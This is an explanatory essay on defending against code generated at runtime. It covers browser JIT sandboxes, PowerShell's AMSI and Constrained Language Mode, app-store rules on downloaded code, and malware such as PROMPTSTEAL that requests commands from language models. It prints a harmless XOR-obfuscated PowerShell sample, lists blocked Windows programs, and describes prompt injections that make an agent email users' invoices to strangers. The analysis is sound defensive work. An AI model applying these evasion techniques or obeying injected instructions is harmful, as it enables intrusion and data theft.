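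WebAssembly is a compact format that lets browsers run programs written in languages such as C++. V8 normally compiles it to machine code, which ACG forbids, so Microsoft (2022) introduced an interpreter for it called DrumBrake. *Enhanced Insecurity Mode* (Wang and Chen, 2026) reported 23 flaws in DrumBrake, found over a year, that let an attacker run code on the victim's computer. In some cases the interpreter failed to stop when it should have. Microsoft has patched all 23. For sites that used WebAssembly, the safer mode therefore removed compiler bugs but added interpreter bugs. An interpreter is usually simpler than an optimising compiler, but DrumBrake was new, while V8's compilers had already been through years of attacks and repairs.

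### Confining the engine's memory

Google kept the compiler in Chrome and tried to limit the damage from its mistakes. When attackers exploit V8, they almost always begin by corrupting memory in its heap, the area where the engine stores a page's objects. The V8 sandbox is meant to keep that corruption from spreading to the rest of the process. (This is a smaller enclosure inside the content process, which has a sandbox of its own.)

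Take a list that a script has created. The engine stores the memory address where the list's contents begin. If an attacker uses a bug to overwrite that address, the "list" can start anywhere in the process, and ordinary JavaScript can then read or change whatever is there. With the sandbox, the engine stores a distance from a fixed starting point instead:

$$\text{address} = \text{base} + \text{offset}, \qquad 0 \le \text{offset} < 2^{40}.$$

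The offset has only 40 bits, so whatever number the attacker writes, the result falls within the same one-terabyte range of addresses. For objects outside that range, the engine stores an index into a protected table that holds their real addresses.

The extra steps slow typical workloads by about 1% or less, far less than giving up the compiler would. They don't stop every attack, because code outside the sandbox still uses numbers stored inside it. For example, the engine might reserve space for an object's property names using one stored count and fill the space using another. An attacker who changes one of the counts can make the names overflow into memory outside the sandbox. Developers can prevent this with an explicit check, and V8's developers found that nearly all the holes discovered by 2024 were simple mistakes of this kind. Ordinary memory-safety tools can catch these mistakes,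 unlike most compiler bugs.

The sandbox is also easier to test than a compiler, because the tester doesn't have to find a compiler bug first. The design assumes that an attacker already controls the heap, so V8 can let test code read and write anywhere inside the sandbox and then detect whether anything outside it gets damaged. According to *The V8 Heap Sandbox* (2024), an OffensiveCon talk by one of the sandbox's engineers, a typical attack on Chrome now requires a flaw in V8, another in the V8 sandbox and a third in the sandbox around the content process. When Google added the V8 sandbox to Chrome's bug bounty programme in 2024, the developers still listed problems to solve before it would be a strong barrier.

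### Permission to generate code on the iPhone

The iPhone applies code signing more strictly than a PC does. An app's signature covers a list of hashes, one for each page of its code. When iOS loads a page, it computes the page's hash and compares it with the list, so it can detect a changed page even after the app has started. An ordinary app can't generate new code in memory and run it, because iOS won't make an unsigned page executable.

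Safari needs an exception to run the unsigned code its JIT compiler produces. Apple grants this exception to Safari's content process through an entitlement, a special permission recorded in a program's signature. For years Apple reserved this permission for its own software. Other iPhone browsers, including Chrome and Firefox, had to use WebKit, which compiled their pages in a process separate from the app.

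The EU's Digital Markets Act forced Apple to allow other browser engines, and since iOS 17.4 in 2024 their developers have been able to apply for access to JIT compilation. Daring Fireball argued that Apple had little choice but to limit this access to trusted browser makers, because rival engines would have been unacceptably slow without it and giving it to every developer would have been insecure.

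Apple's *Using alternative browser engines in the European Union* requires developers of these engines to use memory-safe languages or equivalent features for code that handles web content, split the browser into separate processes and promptly repair flaws that attackers are exploiting. The engine must also pass 90% of a standard set of web tests and 80% of Test262, the JavaScript test suite, with the JIT compiler on or off. Apple offers similar access in Japan from iOS 26.2, where *Using alternative browser engines in Japan* also requires specific hardware-assisted memory protections. These conditions govern how developers build and maintain the engine. None of them involves Apple inspecting the machine code that the engine will generate, which would be impossible.

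So far the new rules have had little practical effect. According to *Conditions and disputes over alternative browser engines on iOS in the EU* (2026), a digest from the anoni.net community, Mozilla wrote on 20 November 2026 that nobody had yet launched an iPhone browser with an engine other than WebKit. Mozilla's main example of the difficulty is that existing Firefox users couldn't switch to its own engine through an update, but would have to install a second Firefox and move their bookmarks and passwords across. Apple's published EU terms require a browser with its own engine to be an EU-only product, which would be enough to cause this problem.

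Apple has blamed the browser makers. At a workshop, it said that Google and Mozilla had "everything they need" and had chosen not to proceed, according to an account by the campaign group Open Web Advocacy quoted in *Apple’s Browser Engine Ban Persists, Even Under the DMA* (Tsai, 2025). On 23 November 2026 the group published an open letter, signed by Mozilla, Brave and the Tor Project among others, asking the European Commission to begin formal enforcement. The Commission answered that it was in talks with Apple but didn't commit to formal proceedings, according to *Apple's conditions for other iOS browser engines in the EU* (2026).

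### Compilers and language models

Browser makers couldn't approve generated code in advance, so they isolated the compiler, limited what the generated code could reach, or stopped generating it. It is tempting to treat a language model as one more generator and copy these defences. The comparison holds up to a point, but a compiler has a precise specification. If $C$ is the compiler, then for every script $s$ and input $x$,

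$$\text{run}(C(s), x) = \text{interpret}(s, x).$$

Developers can therefore test the compiler automatically by generating millions of random scripts, running each one both ways and investigating any difference. They don't need to work out the correct answers first. Test262 adds cases whose answers come from the language standard. Despite this testing, compilers still account for about half of V8's exploited bugs, and JIT spraying worked even though the compiler's answers were correct.

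The command from the agent reading the accounts mailbox can't be checked against a formal definition of its user's request, because none exists. Comparing the command with one from a second model might catch some mistakes, but both models can make the same mistake or follow the same hidden instruction in an email.

The agent also needs more power than a web page. A page can do most of its work without seeing the user's files, so a browser can withhold them. An agent that handles invoices has to read them and may have to send replies. Isolating the generator doesn't help much by itself either. A commercial model usually runs on its provider's servers, much further from the company's files than Edge's compiler process was from the page, but the command it writes still runs on the company's computer.

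## PowerShell and approved programs that run unapproved scripts

A command that an agent writes still needs a program to run it. On Windows this is often PowerShell, a command shell and scripting language that comes with the system and that administrators use for automation. Microsoft signs PowerShell, and practically every Windows allowlist approves it. The check on `powershell.exe` passes no matter what script someone runs, because the script counts only as data, like a document opened in Word.

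A script doesn't even have to be a file, because PowerShell also accepts commands that a person types or another program hands over.

Windows relies on interpreters to enforce its controls on scripts. According to Microsoft's *Security considerations for AppLocker*, a guide to the allowlisting feature that came with Windows 7, an interpreter must check with AppLocker before running a script and then apply the result. Some interpreters don't make this check. Most of Microsoft's fixes therefore involved changing PowerShell itself.

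### How often malware uses installed programs

In *Survivalism* (2021), Barr-Smith, Ugarte-Pedrero and colleagues measured how often Windows malware lives off the land. They collected 31,805,549 program files, including harmless ones for comparison. The scanning service VirusTotal had reports of what about half of these files did when run on an isolated test machine. The researchers searched the reports for commands that started a legitimate program already on the machine or a signed administration tool, and used the rest of each command to work out why the program was started.

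On average, 9.41% of ordinary malware samples used such a program, compared with 2.05% of harmless files. The rate was 26.26% in a set of malware from advanced persistent threats, which are skilled and often state-backed attackers.

These figures cover more than unapproved scripts. A sample counted if it used `reg` to change a Windows setting, or `ping` just to wait a few seconds. Running other code through a trusted program was one of the most common purposes, but PowerShell doesn't appear in the paper's lists of the most frequently used programs. The study left out attackers who type commands or run scripts by hand after breaking in. The Center for Internet Security's *Living off the Land* lists PowerShell among the built-in tools that attackers commonly abuse.

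Barr-Smith and colleagues also tested ten popular antivirus products. They used six Windows programs to open a reverse shell, a connection that lets someone elsewhere run commands on the machine. The products detected the attack in four of the 60 combinations of product and program. Nine months later, after the researchers had told the vendors, the products detected 25. But when the researchers changed or disguised the payload and kept the command lines the same, 19 of those 25 attacks worked again. Some vendors had learned to recognise only the payload, not the command lines that delivered it. Others said that stricter rules would raise too many false alarms, since administrators use the same programs every day.

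### A harmless script in disguise

A small script from Microsoft's *PowerShell ♥ the Blue Team* (2015) shows what the file check misses and what each repair adds. It hides its only real command in a scrambled string. A function called `SuperDecrypt` unscrambles the string, and `Invoke-Expression`, PowerShell's command for running text as code, runs the result. The last two lines, with the string shortened, are:

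```
$decrypted = SuperDecrypt "FUIwQitCNkIn..."
Invoke-Expression $decrypted
```

The string is in Base64, which writes arbitrary bytes as ordinary letters, digits and a few symbols. `SuperDecrypt` converts it back to bytes and combines each one with a fixed key using XOR, an operation that flips a bit wherever the key has a 1. In hexadecimal notation, the first byte is 15 and the key is 42:

$$15_{16} \oplus 42_{16} = 57_{16}.$$

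The result, 57, is the code for the letter W. The whole string becomes `Write-Host 'Pwnd'`, which prints "Pwnd" on the screen.

A static scanner could easily search a file for that command, but this file doesn't contain it. Microsoft's *How the Antimalware Scan Interface (AMSI) helps you defend against malware* describes how malware authors developed such disguises. When scanners searched for a known command, authors split it into two strings and had the script join them. Scanners began joining the strings too, so authors switched to Base64. Most scanners could eventually decode that as well, but they generally couldn't undo custom XOR scrambling.

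Antivirus companies then wrote patterns to detect the disguises themselves. These became the vast majority of their patterns for malicious scripts, but they don't work when a disguise is so simple that many legitimate scripts look the same.

### Scanning the script after it unpacks itself

PowerShell can only run the plain version of a script, however many layers of disguise it has. The Antimalware Scan Interface (AMSI), which Microsoft introduced with Windows 10, lets antivirus software scan that version. Before PowerShell runs a piece of code, it passes the text through AMSI to the installed antivirus product, which can block the code. If a script generates more code as it runs, PowerShell submits that code too.

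In the example, the scanner first receives the function and the scrambled string. When the script reaches `Invoke-Expression`, the scanner receives `Write-Host 'Pwnd'`, which a simple pattern for that command would now match. The pattern would match whether a person typed the line, a function unscrambled it or malware requested it from a language model.

As in an ordinary virus scan, the scanner still has to recognise the command as harmful. Security researchers have also found ways to bypass scan hooks such as AMSI.

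Any program can call AMSI, and any antivirus product can receive the calls. text/plain's *Defensive Technology* (2024) lists the Windows components that call AMSI by default, including the older script hosts `wscript` and `cscript` and the .NET platform, on which PowerShell is built. Office logs the Windows functions that a macro calls, and pauses the macro when it reaches a call that Microsoft considers high-risk. Office then sends the log through AMSI to the scanner, which can assess the macro partly by what it has done so far.

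### Recording the code that ran

Script block logging, which appeared at about the same time, records code without stopping it. A script block is PowerShell's basic unit of code, such as a typed command or the body of a function. The example produces four log entries:

1. the definition of `SuperDecrypt`;
2. the line that calls it with the scrambled string;
3. `Invoke-Expression $decrypted`;
4. `Write-Host 'Pwnd'`.

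An investigator can read the fourth entry without first removing the obfuscation. For code generated at runtime, this is more useful than a record of program hashes, which would show only that PowerShell had run.

Unless an administrator turns on full logging, PowerShell logs only blocks with content that malicious scripts often use. Microsoft called this default a record of last resort, because most companies discovered that they needed the log only when it was too late. An attacker can flood the log with meaningless entries until the old ones disappear, so Microsoft advises copying entries to another machine as soon as possible. The copies need protection too, since scripts can contain sensitive data.

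The log isn't attestation either. It comes from the machine under investigation, and an attacker who gains administrator rights there can switch it off.

### Limiting what a script can call

Constrained Language Mode restricts what code can do, whether or not it looks harmful. It works with App Control, the newer allowlisting feature that Microsoft recommends over AppLocker. Microsoft's *How App Control works with PowerShell* describes the process. When an allowlist is in force, PowerShell queries Windows about each script file before running it. Approved scripts run in full language mode, with a few restrictions. Unapproved scripts run in constrained mode, or not at all if the policy forbids them. Commands that a user types always run in constrained mode, since nobody could have approved them.

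The restrictions mostly concern .NET, whose library gives PowerShell much of its power. In full mode, a script can compile new .NET code and call Windows functions directly, which lets it load a program into memory without saving it to disk. Constrained mode stops scripts from compiling such code, creating objects of unapproved types, or calling those objects' methods. Ordinary PowerShell commands remain available.

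If the example arrives in a file the company has approved, it runs in full. Otherwise it runs in constrained mode, which may block the .NET methods `SuperDecrypt` uses to decode the string and convert the bytes to text. If any of those calls is blocked, the hidden command never appears. If all of them are allowed, `Invoke-Expression` runs the decoded line, also in constrained mode, and nothing in Microsoft's list of restrictions stops a script from printing a word.

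Nothing in that list stops a script from deleting a folder of invoices either, as long as the user has permission to delete it. Constrained mode removes the operations that would let a script escape the allowlist, but a script can still do plenty of damage with the operations that remain.

The restrictions also interfere with legitimate software. Microsoft Defender for Endpoint, a security product for businesses, relies on PowerShell scripts. Microsoft tells administrators to add a rule approving the publisher of those scripts, because some Defender features don't work properly without it. Approving everything in a folder is easier, but Microsoft warns against doing this where ordinary users can add files.

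Constrained mode also depends on PowerShell correctly checking whether a policy restricts the script. Patch My PC, a software company, found that Windows 11 24H2 ran scripts in full language mode under the same default AppLocker rules that had constrained them in the previous version, 23H2.

### Microsoft's list of its own programs to block

The fourth repair, the blocklist of signed Microsoft programs that the Essential Eight requires from Maturity Level Two, goes back to checking files. Microsoft compiled the list with outside researchers and now publishes it in *Application Control for Windows* under the heading "Applications that can bypass App Control and how to block them".

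BornCity's *Windows Defender Application Control* (2022) reproduced the May 2022 version of Microsoft's block list, which had 41 entries. They include `wscript`, which runs VBScript; `mshta`, which runs web pages as programs; `msbuild`, which builds software from source code; `wsl`, which runs Linux programs on Windows; the Linux shell `bash`; and several debuggers. Microsoft recommends blocking everything on the list that an organisation doesn't specifically need. The Canadian Centre for Cyber Security's *Microsoft recommended block rules* (2019) also urged administrators to test and apply the rules for programs they weren't using.

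The list would stop the example only if someone rewrote it for a listed program, for instance in VBScript for `wscript`. The 2022 list doesn't include `powershell.exe`, and Microsoft advises against disabling PowerShell to stop malware, because many administrative jobs depend on it. Blocking `msbuild`, `dotnet` and `bash` would cause a similar problem for software developers, who may use them all day.

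### Batch files and other gaps

The repairs work best for PowerShell. Microsoft's documentation gives a patchier picture for other languages:

| Code | Does AMSI support it? | Can AppLocker control it? |
|---|---|---|
| PowerShell | Yes | Yes |
| VBScript and JScript | Yes | Yes |
| Office macros | Yes, in Microsoft 365 apps | No |
| Batch files | Not listed | Yes |
| Python and Perl scripts | No | No |
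| Programs in the Linux subsystem | Not listed | No |

An administrator can still keep Python off the allowlist. Once the interpreter has approval, though, AppLocker can't choose between the scripts it runs.

Batch files are an older and simpler kind of Windows script, which the command prompt `cmd.exe` runs line by line. App Control doesn't govern them directly. A moderator on Microsoft's support forum, replying to Liming (2025) in *How to block a file type from running using Application Control Policy*, explained that App Control is mainly for compiled programs, while batch files are interpreted text. He recommended AppLocker, which has rules for batch files, but Microsoft now provides only security fixes for it.

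This leaves a gap for organisations following the Essential Eight. Its rules cover scripts too, but Microsoft tells organisations to use App Control from Maturity Level Two, and one that replaced AppLocker entirely would lose AppLocker's rules for batch files. Even AppLocker's rules apply only to files, so they don't cover the same commands typed directly into `cmd.exe`.

### Agents with access to a shell

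For PowerShell, Microsoft moved the check from the file to the moment of execution, when the final code is available to scan or record. It also moved from checking who had approved the code to limiting what unapproved code could do. Both changes also help with agents.

An agent with a shell recreates the original gap, because the company approves the shell but not the commands it runs. A company can approve the scripts its human administrators use regularly and constrain the rest. But an agent may write a new command for every step, so almost everything it does is constrained. If the company relaxes the restrictions to let the agent work, it also relaxes them for commands that come from a malicious email.

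An agent can also bypass these protections unintentionally by writing a script in Python, which AMSI doesn't scan and which has no equivalent of Constrained Language Mode. A scan might not help anyway. If the agent on the accounts mailbox sends the March invoices to the wrong customer, it uses the same commands as when it sends them to the right one, so there is no malware to detect.

Microsoft's 2026 guidance on agents puts more emphasis on containing them. In June, *Windows platform security for AI agents* (2026) acknowledged that agents' behaviour is "often generated at runtime" and announced Microsoft Execution Containers (MXC), a sandbox system that limits which files and network addresses an agent's code can reach. MXC was generally available on Windows 11 by 17 November, when Microsoft published *A guide to governing local AI agents with Intune* (Intune is its service for managing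 employees' devices).

The Intune guide also describes a check based on an app's identity. An administrator can list an unwanted app by its installer or package identifier, and Intune marks any computer that has the app as non-compliant. The company can then block that computer from protected resources, even while the agent is inactive. In the preview version, administrators can't select editor extensions, standalone program files or packages from npm, a popular source of JavaScript software. This is a serious omission because agents can come in any of these forms.

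For agents that the company allows, an administrator uses MXC to limit access. The policy can make a folder off-limits, read-only or writable, and can allow or deny network connections. When an agent requests a container, Windows checks the request against the policy and denies anything beyond those limits. A coding agent might get access to a project folder but not to the folder where the company keeps its passwords.

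Windows enforces these limits whatever code the model writes, but only for agents whose developers have adopted MXC and that Microsoft Defender can identify, starting with GitHub's Copilot CLI and OpenAI's Codex CLI. The agent's harness must send Windows a request before running the code, as a script interpreter must under AppLocker.

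## Apple's review rule and apps that write apps

Apple reviews each iPhone app before release. iOS blocks new unsigned machine code, except in browser engines that have permission to run it. But an app can include an interpreter and download a script that adds a feature without changing any hash. Apple addresses this gap with Guideline 2.5.2, a rule developers must accept, which is meant to keep apps the same after review. In 2026, Apple enforced it against apps that use an AI model to write other apps.

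### What Guideline 2.5.2 forbids

Apple's *App Review Guidelines* require an app to be self-contained in its bundle, the package of files that the developer submits. The app may not read or write data outside its own storage area. It also may not download, install or execute code that "introduces or changes features or functionality of the app", or of other apps. This last rule applies to scripts as well as machine code, because it depends on what the code does to the app.

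Apple makes an exception for apps that teach programming or let students test code. These apps may download code in limited circumstances if the code serves no other purpose and the user can view and edit all of its source. Apple also allows HTML5 mini apps, small programs made with web technology that run inside a larger app. According to Open Terms Archive's *Apple updates App Store rules on data use, age-gating, external software*, mini apps must follow the store's rules and can't use the phone's native functions without Apple's permission.

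Apple's developer licence is looser than the guideline. One clause, quoted in 9to5Mac's *Developers behind vibe coding app Anything detail next steps*, lets an app download interpreted code as long as the code doesn't change the app's primary purpose. A new feature that fits the advertised purpose would satisfy this clause but still seems to break the guideline.

Guideline 2.5.2 also applies to iPhone apps distributed outside the App Store. In the EU and Japan, developers may use other marketplaces, but Apple still checks those apps against a shorter list of rules that includes 2.5.2.

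Review before release depends on the rule. Suppose Apple approves a recipe app on Monday, and on Tuesday the app downloads a script that turns it into a gambling app. Apple has not reviewed the app that users now have. Apple asks developers to describe every new feature in their notes to the reviewer and to keep their servers running during the review so the reviewer can try everything. That effort is worthwhile only if the features don't change until the next submission.

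### Approved apps that changed later

In *Jekyll on iOS* (2013), Wang, Lu and colleagues showed that an app could pass review and then change its behaviour without loading new machine code. They took an open-source news reader, planted flaws that their server could trigger later, and hid the pieces of unwanted functions among its ordinary code. Apple approved the app after seven days. The researchers installed it on their test devices and immediately withdrew it from the store. Nobody else had installed it, according to Apple's download figures.

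Their server then sent the app specially prepared news items, which made it post tweets, record video and read the device's ID number on the test phones. Its signature remained valid because every instruction it ran had been in the approved file. The server had changed only the order in which the app ran them.

Guideline 2.5.2 is hard to apply to such an app because what it downloads looks like news. Wang and colleagues argued that better reviewing wouldn't solve the problem, because no analysis can find every flaw in every program, and a developer who plants a flaw can disguise it. They reported the method to Apple and called for monitoring apps on the phone while they run. They tested iOS 5 and 6, so their attacks are long out of date, but their argument about review doesn't depend on those particular attacks.

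A dishonest developer can evade review by much simpler means. *Nudification Guidelines and Terminating Developer Accounts* (Tsai, 2026) quotes a WIRED investigation of a network of more than 400 connected apps and web domains. Many of the apps were presented as everyday services such as language tuition or workout coaching, but for some users they loaded a hidden web interface that generated sexual images from uploaded photographs. After each download, the app sent details such as the user's location and language to a server, which selected the version to show, so a reviewer could have seen only the innocent one.

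Apple's rules already banned hidden features, and on 16 October 2026 the company strengthened them against deceptive review practices, as Mendes (2026) reported in *Apple’s new App Store rules crack down on AI nudification*. Tsai objected that App Review can't stop a bait-and-switch, however Apple words the guideline. He is right about the review, but the rule lets Apple remove the app and expel its developer once someone notices the switch. This gives the same after-the-fact accountability as Authenticode, with the same weakness.

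### Replit, Vibecode and Anything

"Vibe coding" means describing a program in ordinary language and letting an AI model write it. Replit, Vibecode and Anything all offered this on the iPhone. A user might ask for a habit tracker, and the app would have a model write one and display it for the user to try. If the user then submits the habit tracker to the App Store, Apple can review it like any other stored code. The preview is harder to review because it runs before anyone at Apple could have seen it.

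The vibe coding app Anything launched on the iPhone in November 2025 without trouble. Apple began blocking its updates in December, according to MacRumors' *Apple Pulls Vibe Coding App 'Anything' From App Store, Escalating Enforcement* (2026). In March 2026, the news site The Information reported that Apple was also holding back updates to Replit and Vibecode.

Apple responded that it had no rule against vibe coding and pointed to Guideline 2.5.2. MacRumors' *Apple Quietly Blocks Updates for Popular 'Vibe Coding' Apps* (2026) describes the changes under discussion for each app. Replit displayed generated apps in a web view, a browser window inside its own app, and expected approval if it opened them in an external browser instead. Apple's reviewers indicated that they would probably approve Vibecode's updates if the app stopped generating software for Apple devices.

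Anything's co-founder Dhruv Amin also tried moving the previews to a web browser. Apple blocked that update and removed the app from the store on 26 March. The app returned on 3 April but had disappeared again by the following Monday, according to AppleInsider's *Vibe coding app's victory lap cut very short by the App Store*. Anything's developers wrote that they had tried four technical approaches and Apple had rejected each one. AIChief's *How vibe coding app Anything is mounting a comeback* adds that the second removal came after Apple had told the company it couldn't market itself as an "app maker". The developers switched to taking requests by text message and building the apps in the cloud, and announced a desktop companion for previews.

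Replit's dispute ended better for the company. At the end of April its chief executive, Amjad Masad, denied that the app downloaded new code after approval. He called Apple's justification a lie and said he was willing to prove it in court, according to iClarified's *Replit CEO Says Apple's App Store Block Justification Is a 'Total Lie'* (2026). On 15 May he announced that the companies had "worked things out" and that Replit had released its first update in four months. AppleInsider's *Apple's treatment of AI coding apps could be shifting with Replit update* (2026) notes that neither company explained whether Replit had changed its previews.

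Other developers therefore learned little from the approval. The private agreement also meant that no court had to decide what Guideline 2.5.2 covers. Apple revised its guidelines in June, but the list of revised sections in thenote.app's *Apple Developer* doesn't include 2.5.2. The announced purpose of the October changes was to deal with harmful content and deceptive developers. At the end of 2026, a company planning a similar app still had to guess which kinds of preview Apple would accept.

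### Safety, late enforcement and competition

Apple argues that people who install an app from its store rely on Apple having examined it, and nobody has examined code that a model wrote a moment ago. Review also can't keep up with such code. Apple's chief executive, Tim Cook, said in June that developers were already making well over 1,000 submissions an hour, according to 9to5Mac's *Apple tightens App Review Guidelines against apps that ‘do not add value’*, and a vibe coding app can produce a new version every time the user changes the prompt.

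Amin says Apple also raised two risks in a call: that Anything might download malicious code, and that a user might build a harmful app with it, install that app outside the store and falsely claim that it had passed review. Guideline 2.5.2 is meant to address the first risk. The second is a weaker reason to single out Anything, since someone could write the same harmful app on a Mac and make the same false claim.

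An app can connect its web view to its own functions, so that a page inside it can request a photograph or the user's contacts. A page in Safari has no such connection to the app that opened it. This difference would be a sound security reason for opening previews in an external browser, the change Replit discussed, even though the same JavaScript runs on the same phone. But it makes Apple's refusal of Anything's browser version harder to understand.

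Critics can point out that web views have run unreviewed JavaScript for years. When a news app opens a link in a web view, it runs whatever script the website sends, and Apple doesn't review the website. Tsai (2026), in *Updates to Vibe Coding Apps Rejected From the App Store*, asks why Apple blocked updates to vibe coding apps if they had broken a longstanding rule from the start. He quotes a report that v0, a similar app from Vercel, didn't face the same restrictions.

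A change log from cur.at (2018) shows that the rule's key phrase was already in place in June 2018. Tsai also links to his older posts, including some about disputes over the Python editor Pythonista and the emulator iDOS. Apple seems to have enforced an old rule late and unevenly, which is still a serious problem for a company that built its product around an earlier approval.

Apple also competes with these tools. It announced AI agents for Xcode, its own program for writing apps, on 3 February 2026, while it was blocking Anything's updates. Replit fell from first to third among free developer tools in Apple's rankings after its last update in January, which it partly blamed on the block. The timing doesn't prove a motive, since a restriction can protect both users and Apple's revenue. The request to Vibecode is the hardest to explain by safety alone. Software for Apple devices has to pass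 Apple's review before it reaches the App Store, but web apps don't need that review, and Vibecode could apparently have kept generating them.

### Google's rules for Android apps and Chrome extensions

Google has two rules on the same problem, and they differ from each other as much as from Apple's. Its *Device and Network Abuse* policy bars apps on Google Play, the main Android store, from downloading executable code, such as compiled Android libraries, from outside the store. The policy exempts code that runs in an interpreter or virtual machine with only indirect access to Android's functions, such as JavaScript in a web view.

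Under the exemption, interpreted code that an app loads while running must still not allow violations of Google's other policies. Google began enforcing this condition in October 2021, according to TechRadar's *Google cracks down on misuse of JavaScript, Python in Android apps*. Google also forbids apps to load untrusted web content in a web view connected to the app's own functions. Unlike Apple, Google lets downloaded scripts add features, but it restricts what they can reach and holds the developer responsible for what they do.

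The Chrome Web Store, which distributes extensions (small programs that add functions to Google's browser), has the strictest rule of the three. Under Google's *Additional Requirements for Manifest V3*, the rules for the current extension format, reviewers must be able to work out an extension's full functionality easily from the code its developer submits. An extension may fetch data, such as images or a file that switches built-in features on and off, but not logic. Google also forbids developers to build an interpreter for complex commands fetched as data, which would otherwise be a way around the ban.

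Some programs can't work under that restriction, so Google makes a few exceptions. *Deal with remote hosted code violations* explains that extensions that manage users' own scripts can run them through a special interface, but only after the user turns on developer mode. A debugging interface is also allowed, and it displays a warning bar while in use. An extension can also run outside code in a sandboxed frame, a part of a page cut off from the extension's powers, but reviewers must still be able to determine what the whole extension does.

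### An interface written on each launch

Suppose an expenses app, which also comes as a Chrome extension, sends a summary of recent spending to a model on a server every time the user opens it. The model then writes that day's screen, which no reviewer has seen. It might be a chart of restaurant bills on Monday and a form for travel receipts on Tuesday, after the user has booked a flight.

The developer could let the model write JavaScript and run it in a web view or, in the extension, a sandboxed frame. Or the model could choose from parts already built into the app, by returning a short description like this:

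`{"show": "bar_chart", "data": "restaurants", "button": "add_receipt"}`

None of the three rules mentions such an app, but their wording suggests these results:

| Store | Model writes JavaScript | Model chooses built-in parts |
|---|---|---|
| Apple's App Store | Probably forbidden if the script adds a feature, such as the receipt form; unclear if it only changes the layout | Probably allowed, because the reviewed app contains every feature |
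| Google Play | Allowed if the script has only indirect access to Android and can't break other policies | Allowed |
| Chrome Web Store | Forbidden in the extension's own pages; doubtful in a sandboxed frame | Allowed, unless the descriptions grow into a language for complex commands |

The sandboxed frame is doubtful because the extension's functionality depends on what the model writes, and reviewers can't determine that from the submitted files. On Google Play, the developer would have to be confident that no script the model might write could break a policy. Testing a few hundred screens wouldn't establish this, but blocking the web view's access to the camera, the contacts and the rest of the phone would rule out many of the worst results.

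Moving the model onto the phone would remove the download, but the screens would be no more predictable. Apple's rule would still apply because it covers executing code as well as downloading it. Chrome's reviewers would still have to work out everything the extension could do.

Built-in parts suit all three stores better, because a reviewer can try every chart and button in advance. But the reviewer can't try every combination, and the news reader in Wang and colleagues' experiment caused harm by running approved code in a new order. If the expenses app has one part that reads receipts and another that sends email, and the model can use both without asking, a receipt with a hidden instruction could lead the model to email the user's other receipts to a stranger. It would use only functions that Apple had reviewed.

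## Malware that asks a language model for its code

The expenses app contains every function it will use, and a model only chooses among them. Since 2025, security researchers have found malicious programs that don't contain all the code they will run. The file includes a request in plain English, which the program sends to a language model once it is running on the victim's computer, and the model returns code or commands. Antivirus software that scans the file beforehand can examine the request but not the response.

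### How a static scanner judges a file

The oldest method is to search for patterns from known malware. Antivirus companies call these patterns signatures, but they are unrelated to digital signatures. A hash of the whole file is too easy to evade, so analysts prefer a byte sequence that the malware's author is unlikely to change, such as part of a decryption routine. Well-chosen patterns cause few false alarms, but they miss new malware.

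Heuristics are rules about suspicious traits, so they can catch malware that nobody has seen before. A rule might add points if a small program can write into another program's memory, or if most of the file looks random. Scanners measure randomness as entropy. If $p_i$ is the share of the file's bytes that have the value $i$, the entropy in bits per byte is

$$H = -\sum_{i=0}^{255} p_i \log_2 p_i.$$

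English text has an entropy score between 4 and 5, while encrypted or compressed data comes close to the maximum of 8. A high score suggests that the program is packed, which hides its real code until it runs. Ordinary installers are compressed too, so high entropy alone is weak evidence of malware.

A learned classifier learns from examples how much weight to give each trait. Its developers train it on millions of files labelled harmful or harmless, and it gives each new file a score. The vendor sets the score above which the product blocks a file. Suppose a classifier catches 99% of malware and wrongly flags 0.1% of harmless files. A company with a million harmless files and ten malicious ones would get about a thousand false alarms and about ten real ones, so vendors tend to set the threshold high.

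### Why no scanner can be perfect

Fred Cohen showed in *Computer Viruses: Theory and Experiments* (1984) that no program can detect every virus. He defined a virus as a program that can copy itself, possibly in altered form, into other programs. His argument takes three steps:

1. Suppose there is a detector $D$ that can examine any program, always finishes, and always answers correctly whether the program is a virus.
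2. Someone can then write a program $V$ that contains a copy of $D$ and applies it to $V$'s own code.
3. If $D$ answers "virus", $V$ stops without copying itself. If $D$ answers "not a virus", $V$ copies itself into other programs.

In short,

$$V \text{ spreads} \iff D(V) = \text{"not a virus"}.$$

Both answers are wrong, so $D$ can't exist.

Scanners can still be useful because they don't have to be right about every possible program. $V$ defeats one detector, but a different detector, or an analyst's pattern for $V$, could still catch it. A scanner could also block everything it can't clear, much as Linux's eBPF verifier rejects some safe programs, but people would soon uninstall an antivirus product that did this. Malware authors also reuse code and attack many victims, so once a vendor has one copy, it can protect its other customers.

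Cohen's detector failed even though it could examine all of $V$. Malware that uses a model poses a more mundane problem because part of the program isn't in the file. Downloaders, a common type of malware, have always kept code out of the file by fetching a second program from the attacker's server. With a model, the attacker no longer has to write or host the missing code, which can differ on every computer.

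### PROMPTFLUX and PROMPTSTEAL

In November 2025, Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker* described the first malware Google had found that uses a language model while running.

PROMPTFLUX, a VBScript program, contained a decoy installer, code for copying itself to removable drives and shared folders, a prompt, and an API key for Google's Gemini models. Gemini was supposed to reply to the prompt with a newly disguised version of the script, which PROMPTFLUX would save so that it ran whenever the computer started. One variant requested a complete rewrite every hour, so a hash of one copy would not identify the next.

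Each new version would still be a file that a scanner could examine. To rewrite itself again, it would also need the key, the request and the code for contacting Gemini, so the copies would share some features unless the model disguised those too. PROMPTFLUX's author had disabled the self-update function in the sample that Google examined, and Google found no sign that the malware could compromise a victim's computer or network in that state.

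Google found APT28, a group backed by the Russian government, using malware called PROMPTSTEAL against Ukraine in June 2025. The program posed as an image generator. While the user answered its questions about images, it contacted Hugging Face, a platform that hosts openly available models, and requested Windows commands from the model Qwen2.5-Coder. PROMPTSTEAL ran the commands without checking them to collect details of the computer and copy the user's documents, then sent the results to the attackers' server.

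A scan of PROMPTSTEAL's file could find the code that contacts the model and the code that runs its replies, but not the commands themselves, which a scanner's patterns might otherwise match. The scan could also find the request for those commands, which would show a reader what the program was meant to do, but an attacker can reword the request in seconds or scramble it like any other text. Later samples of PROMPTSTEAL added obfuscation.

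### HONESTCUE's harmless request

HONESTCUE, which Google first saw in September 2025, is harder to judge from its file. According to the February 2026 issue of Google Threat Intelligence Group's *GTIG AI Threat Tracker*, it requests C# source code from Gemini, compiles the reply with a standard component of Microsoft's .NET platform, and runs the result in memory, so the generated code is never saved as a program file on disk. That code downloads and starts another piece of malware.

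Google Threat Intelligence Group points out that the stored request is "not malicious in its own right". One version asked only for a program that displays a greeting, presumably as a test. Others asked for a program that downloads something and runs it, as any software updater does. A developer could send the same request on an ordinary working day, and Gemini would have little reason to refuse. The other parts of the attack look just as ordinary:

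| Part of the attack | Where it is before the run | Why a check might pass it |
|---|---|---|
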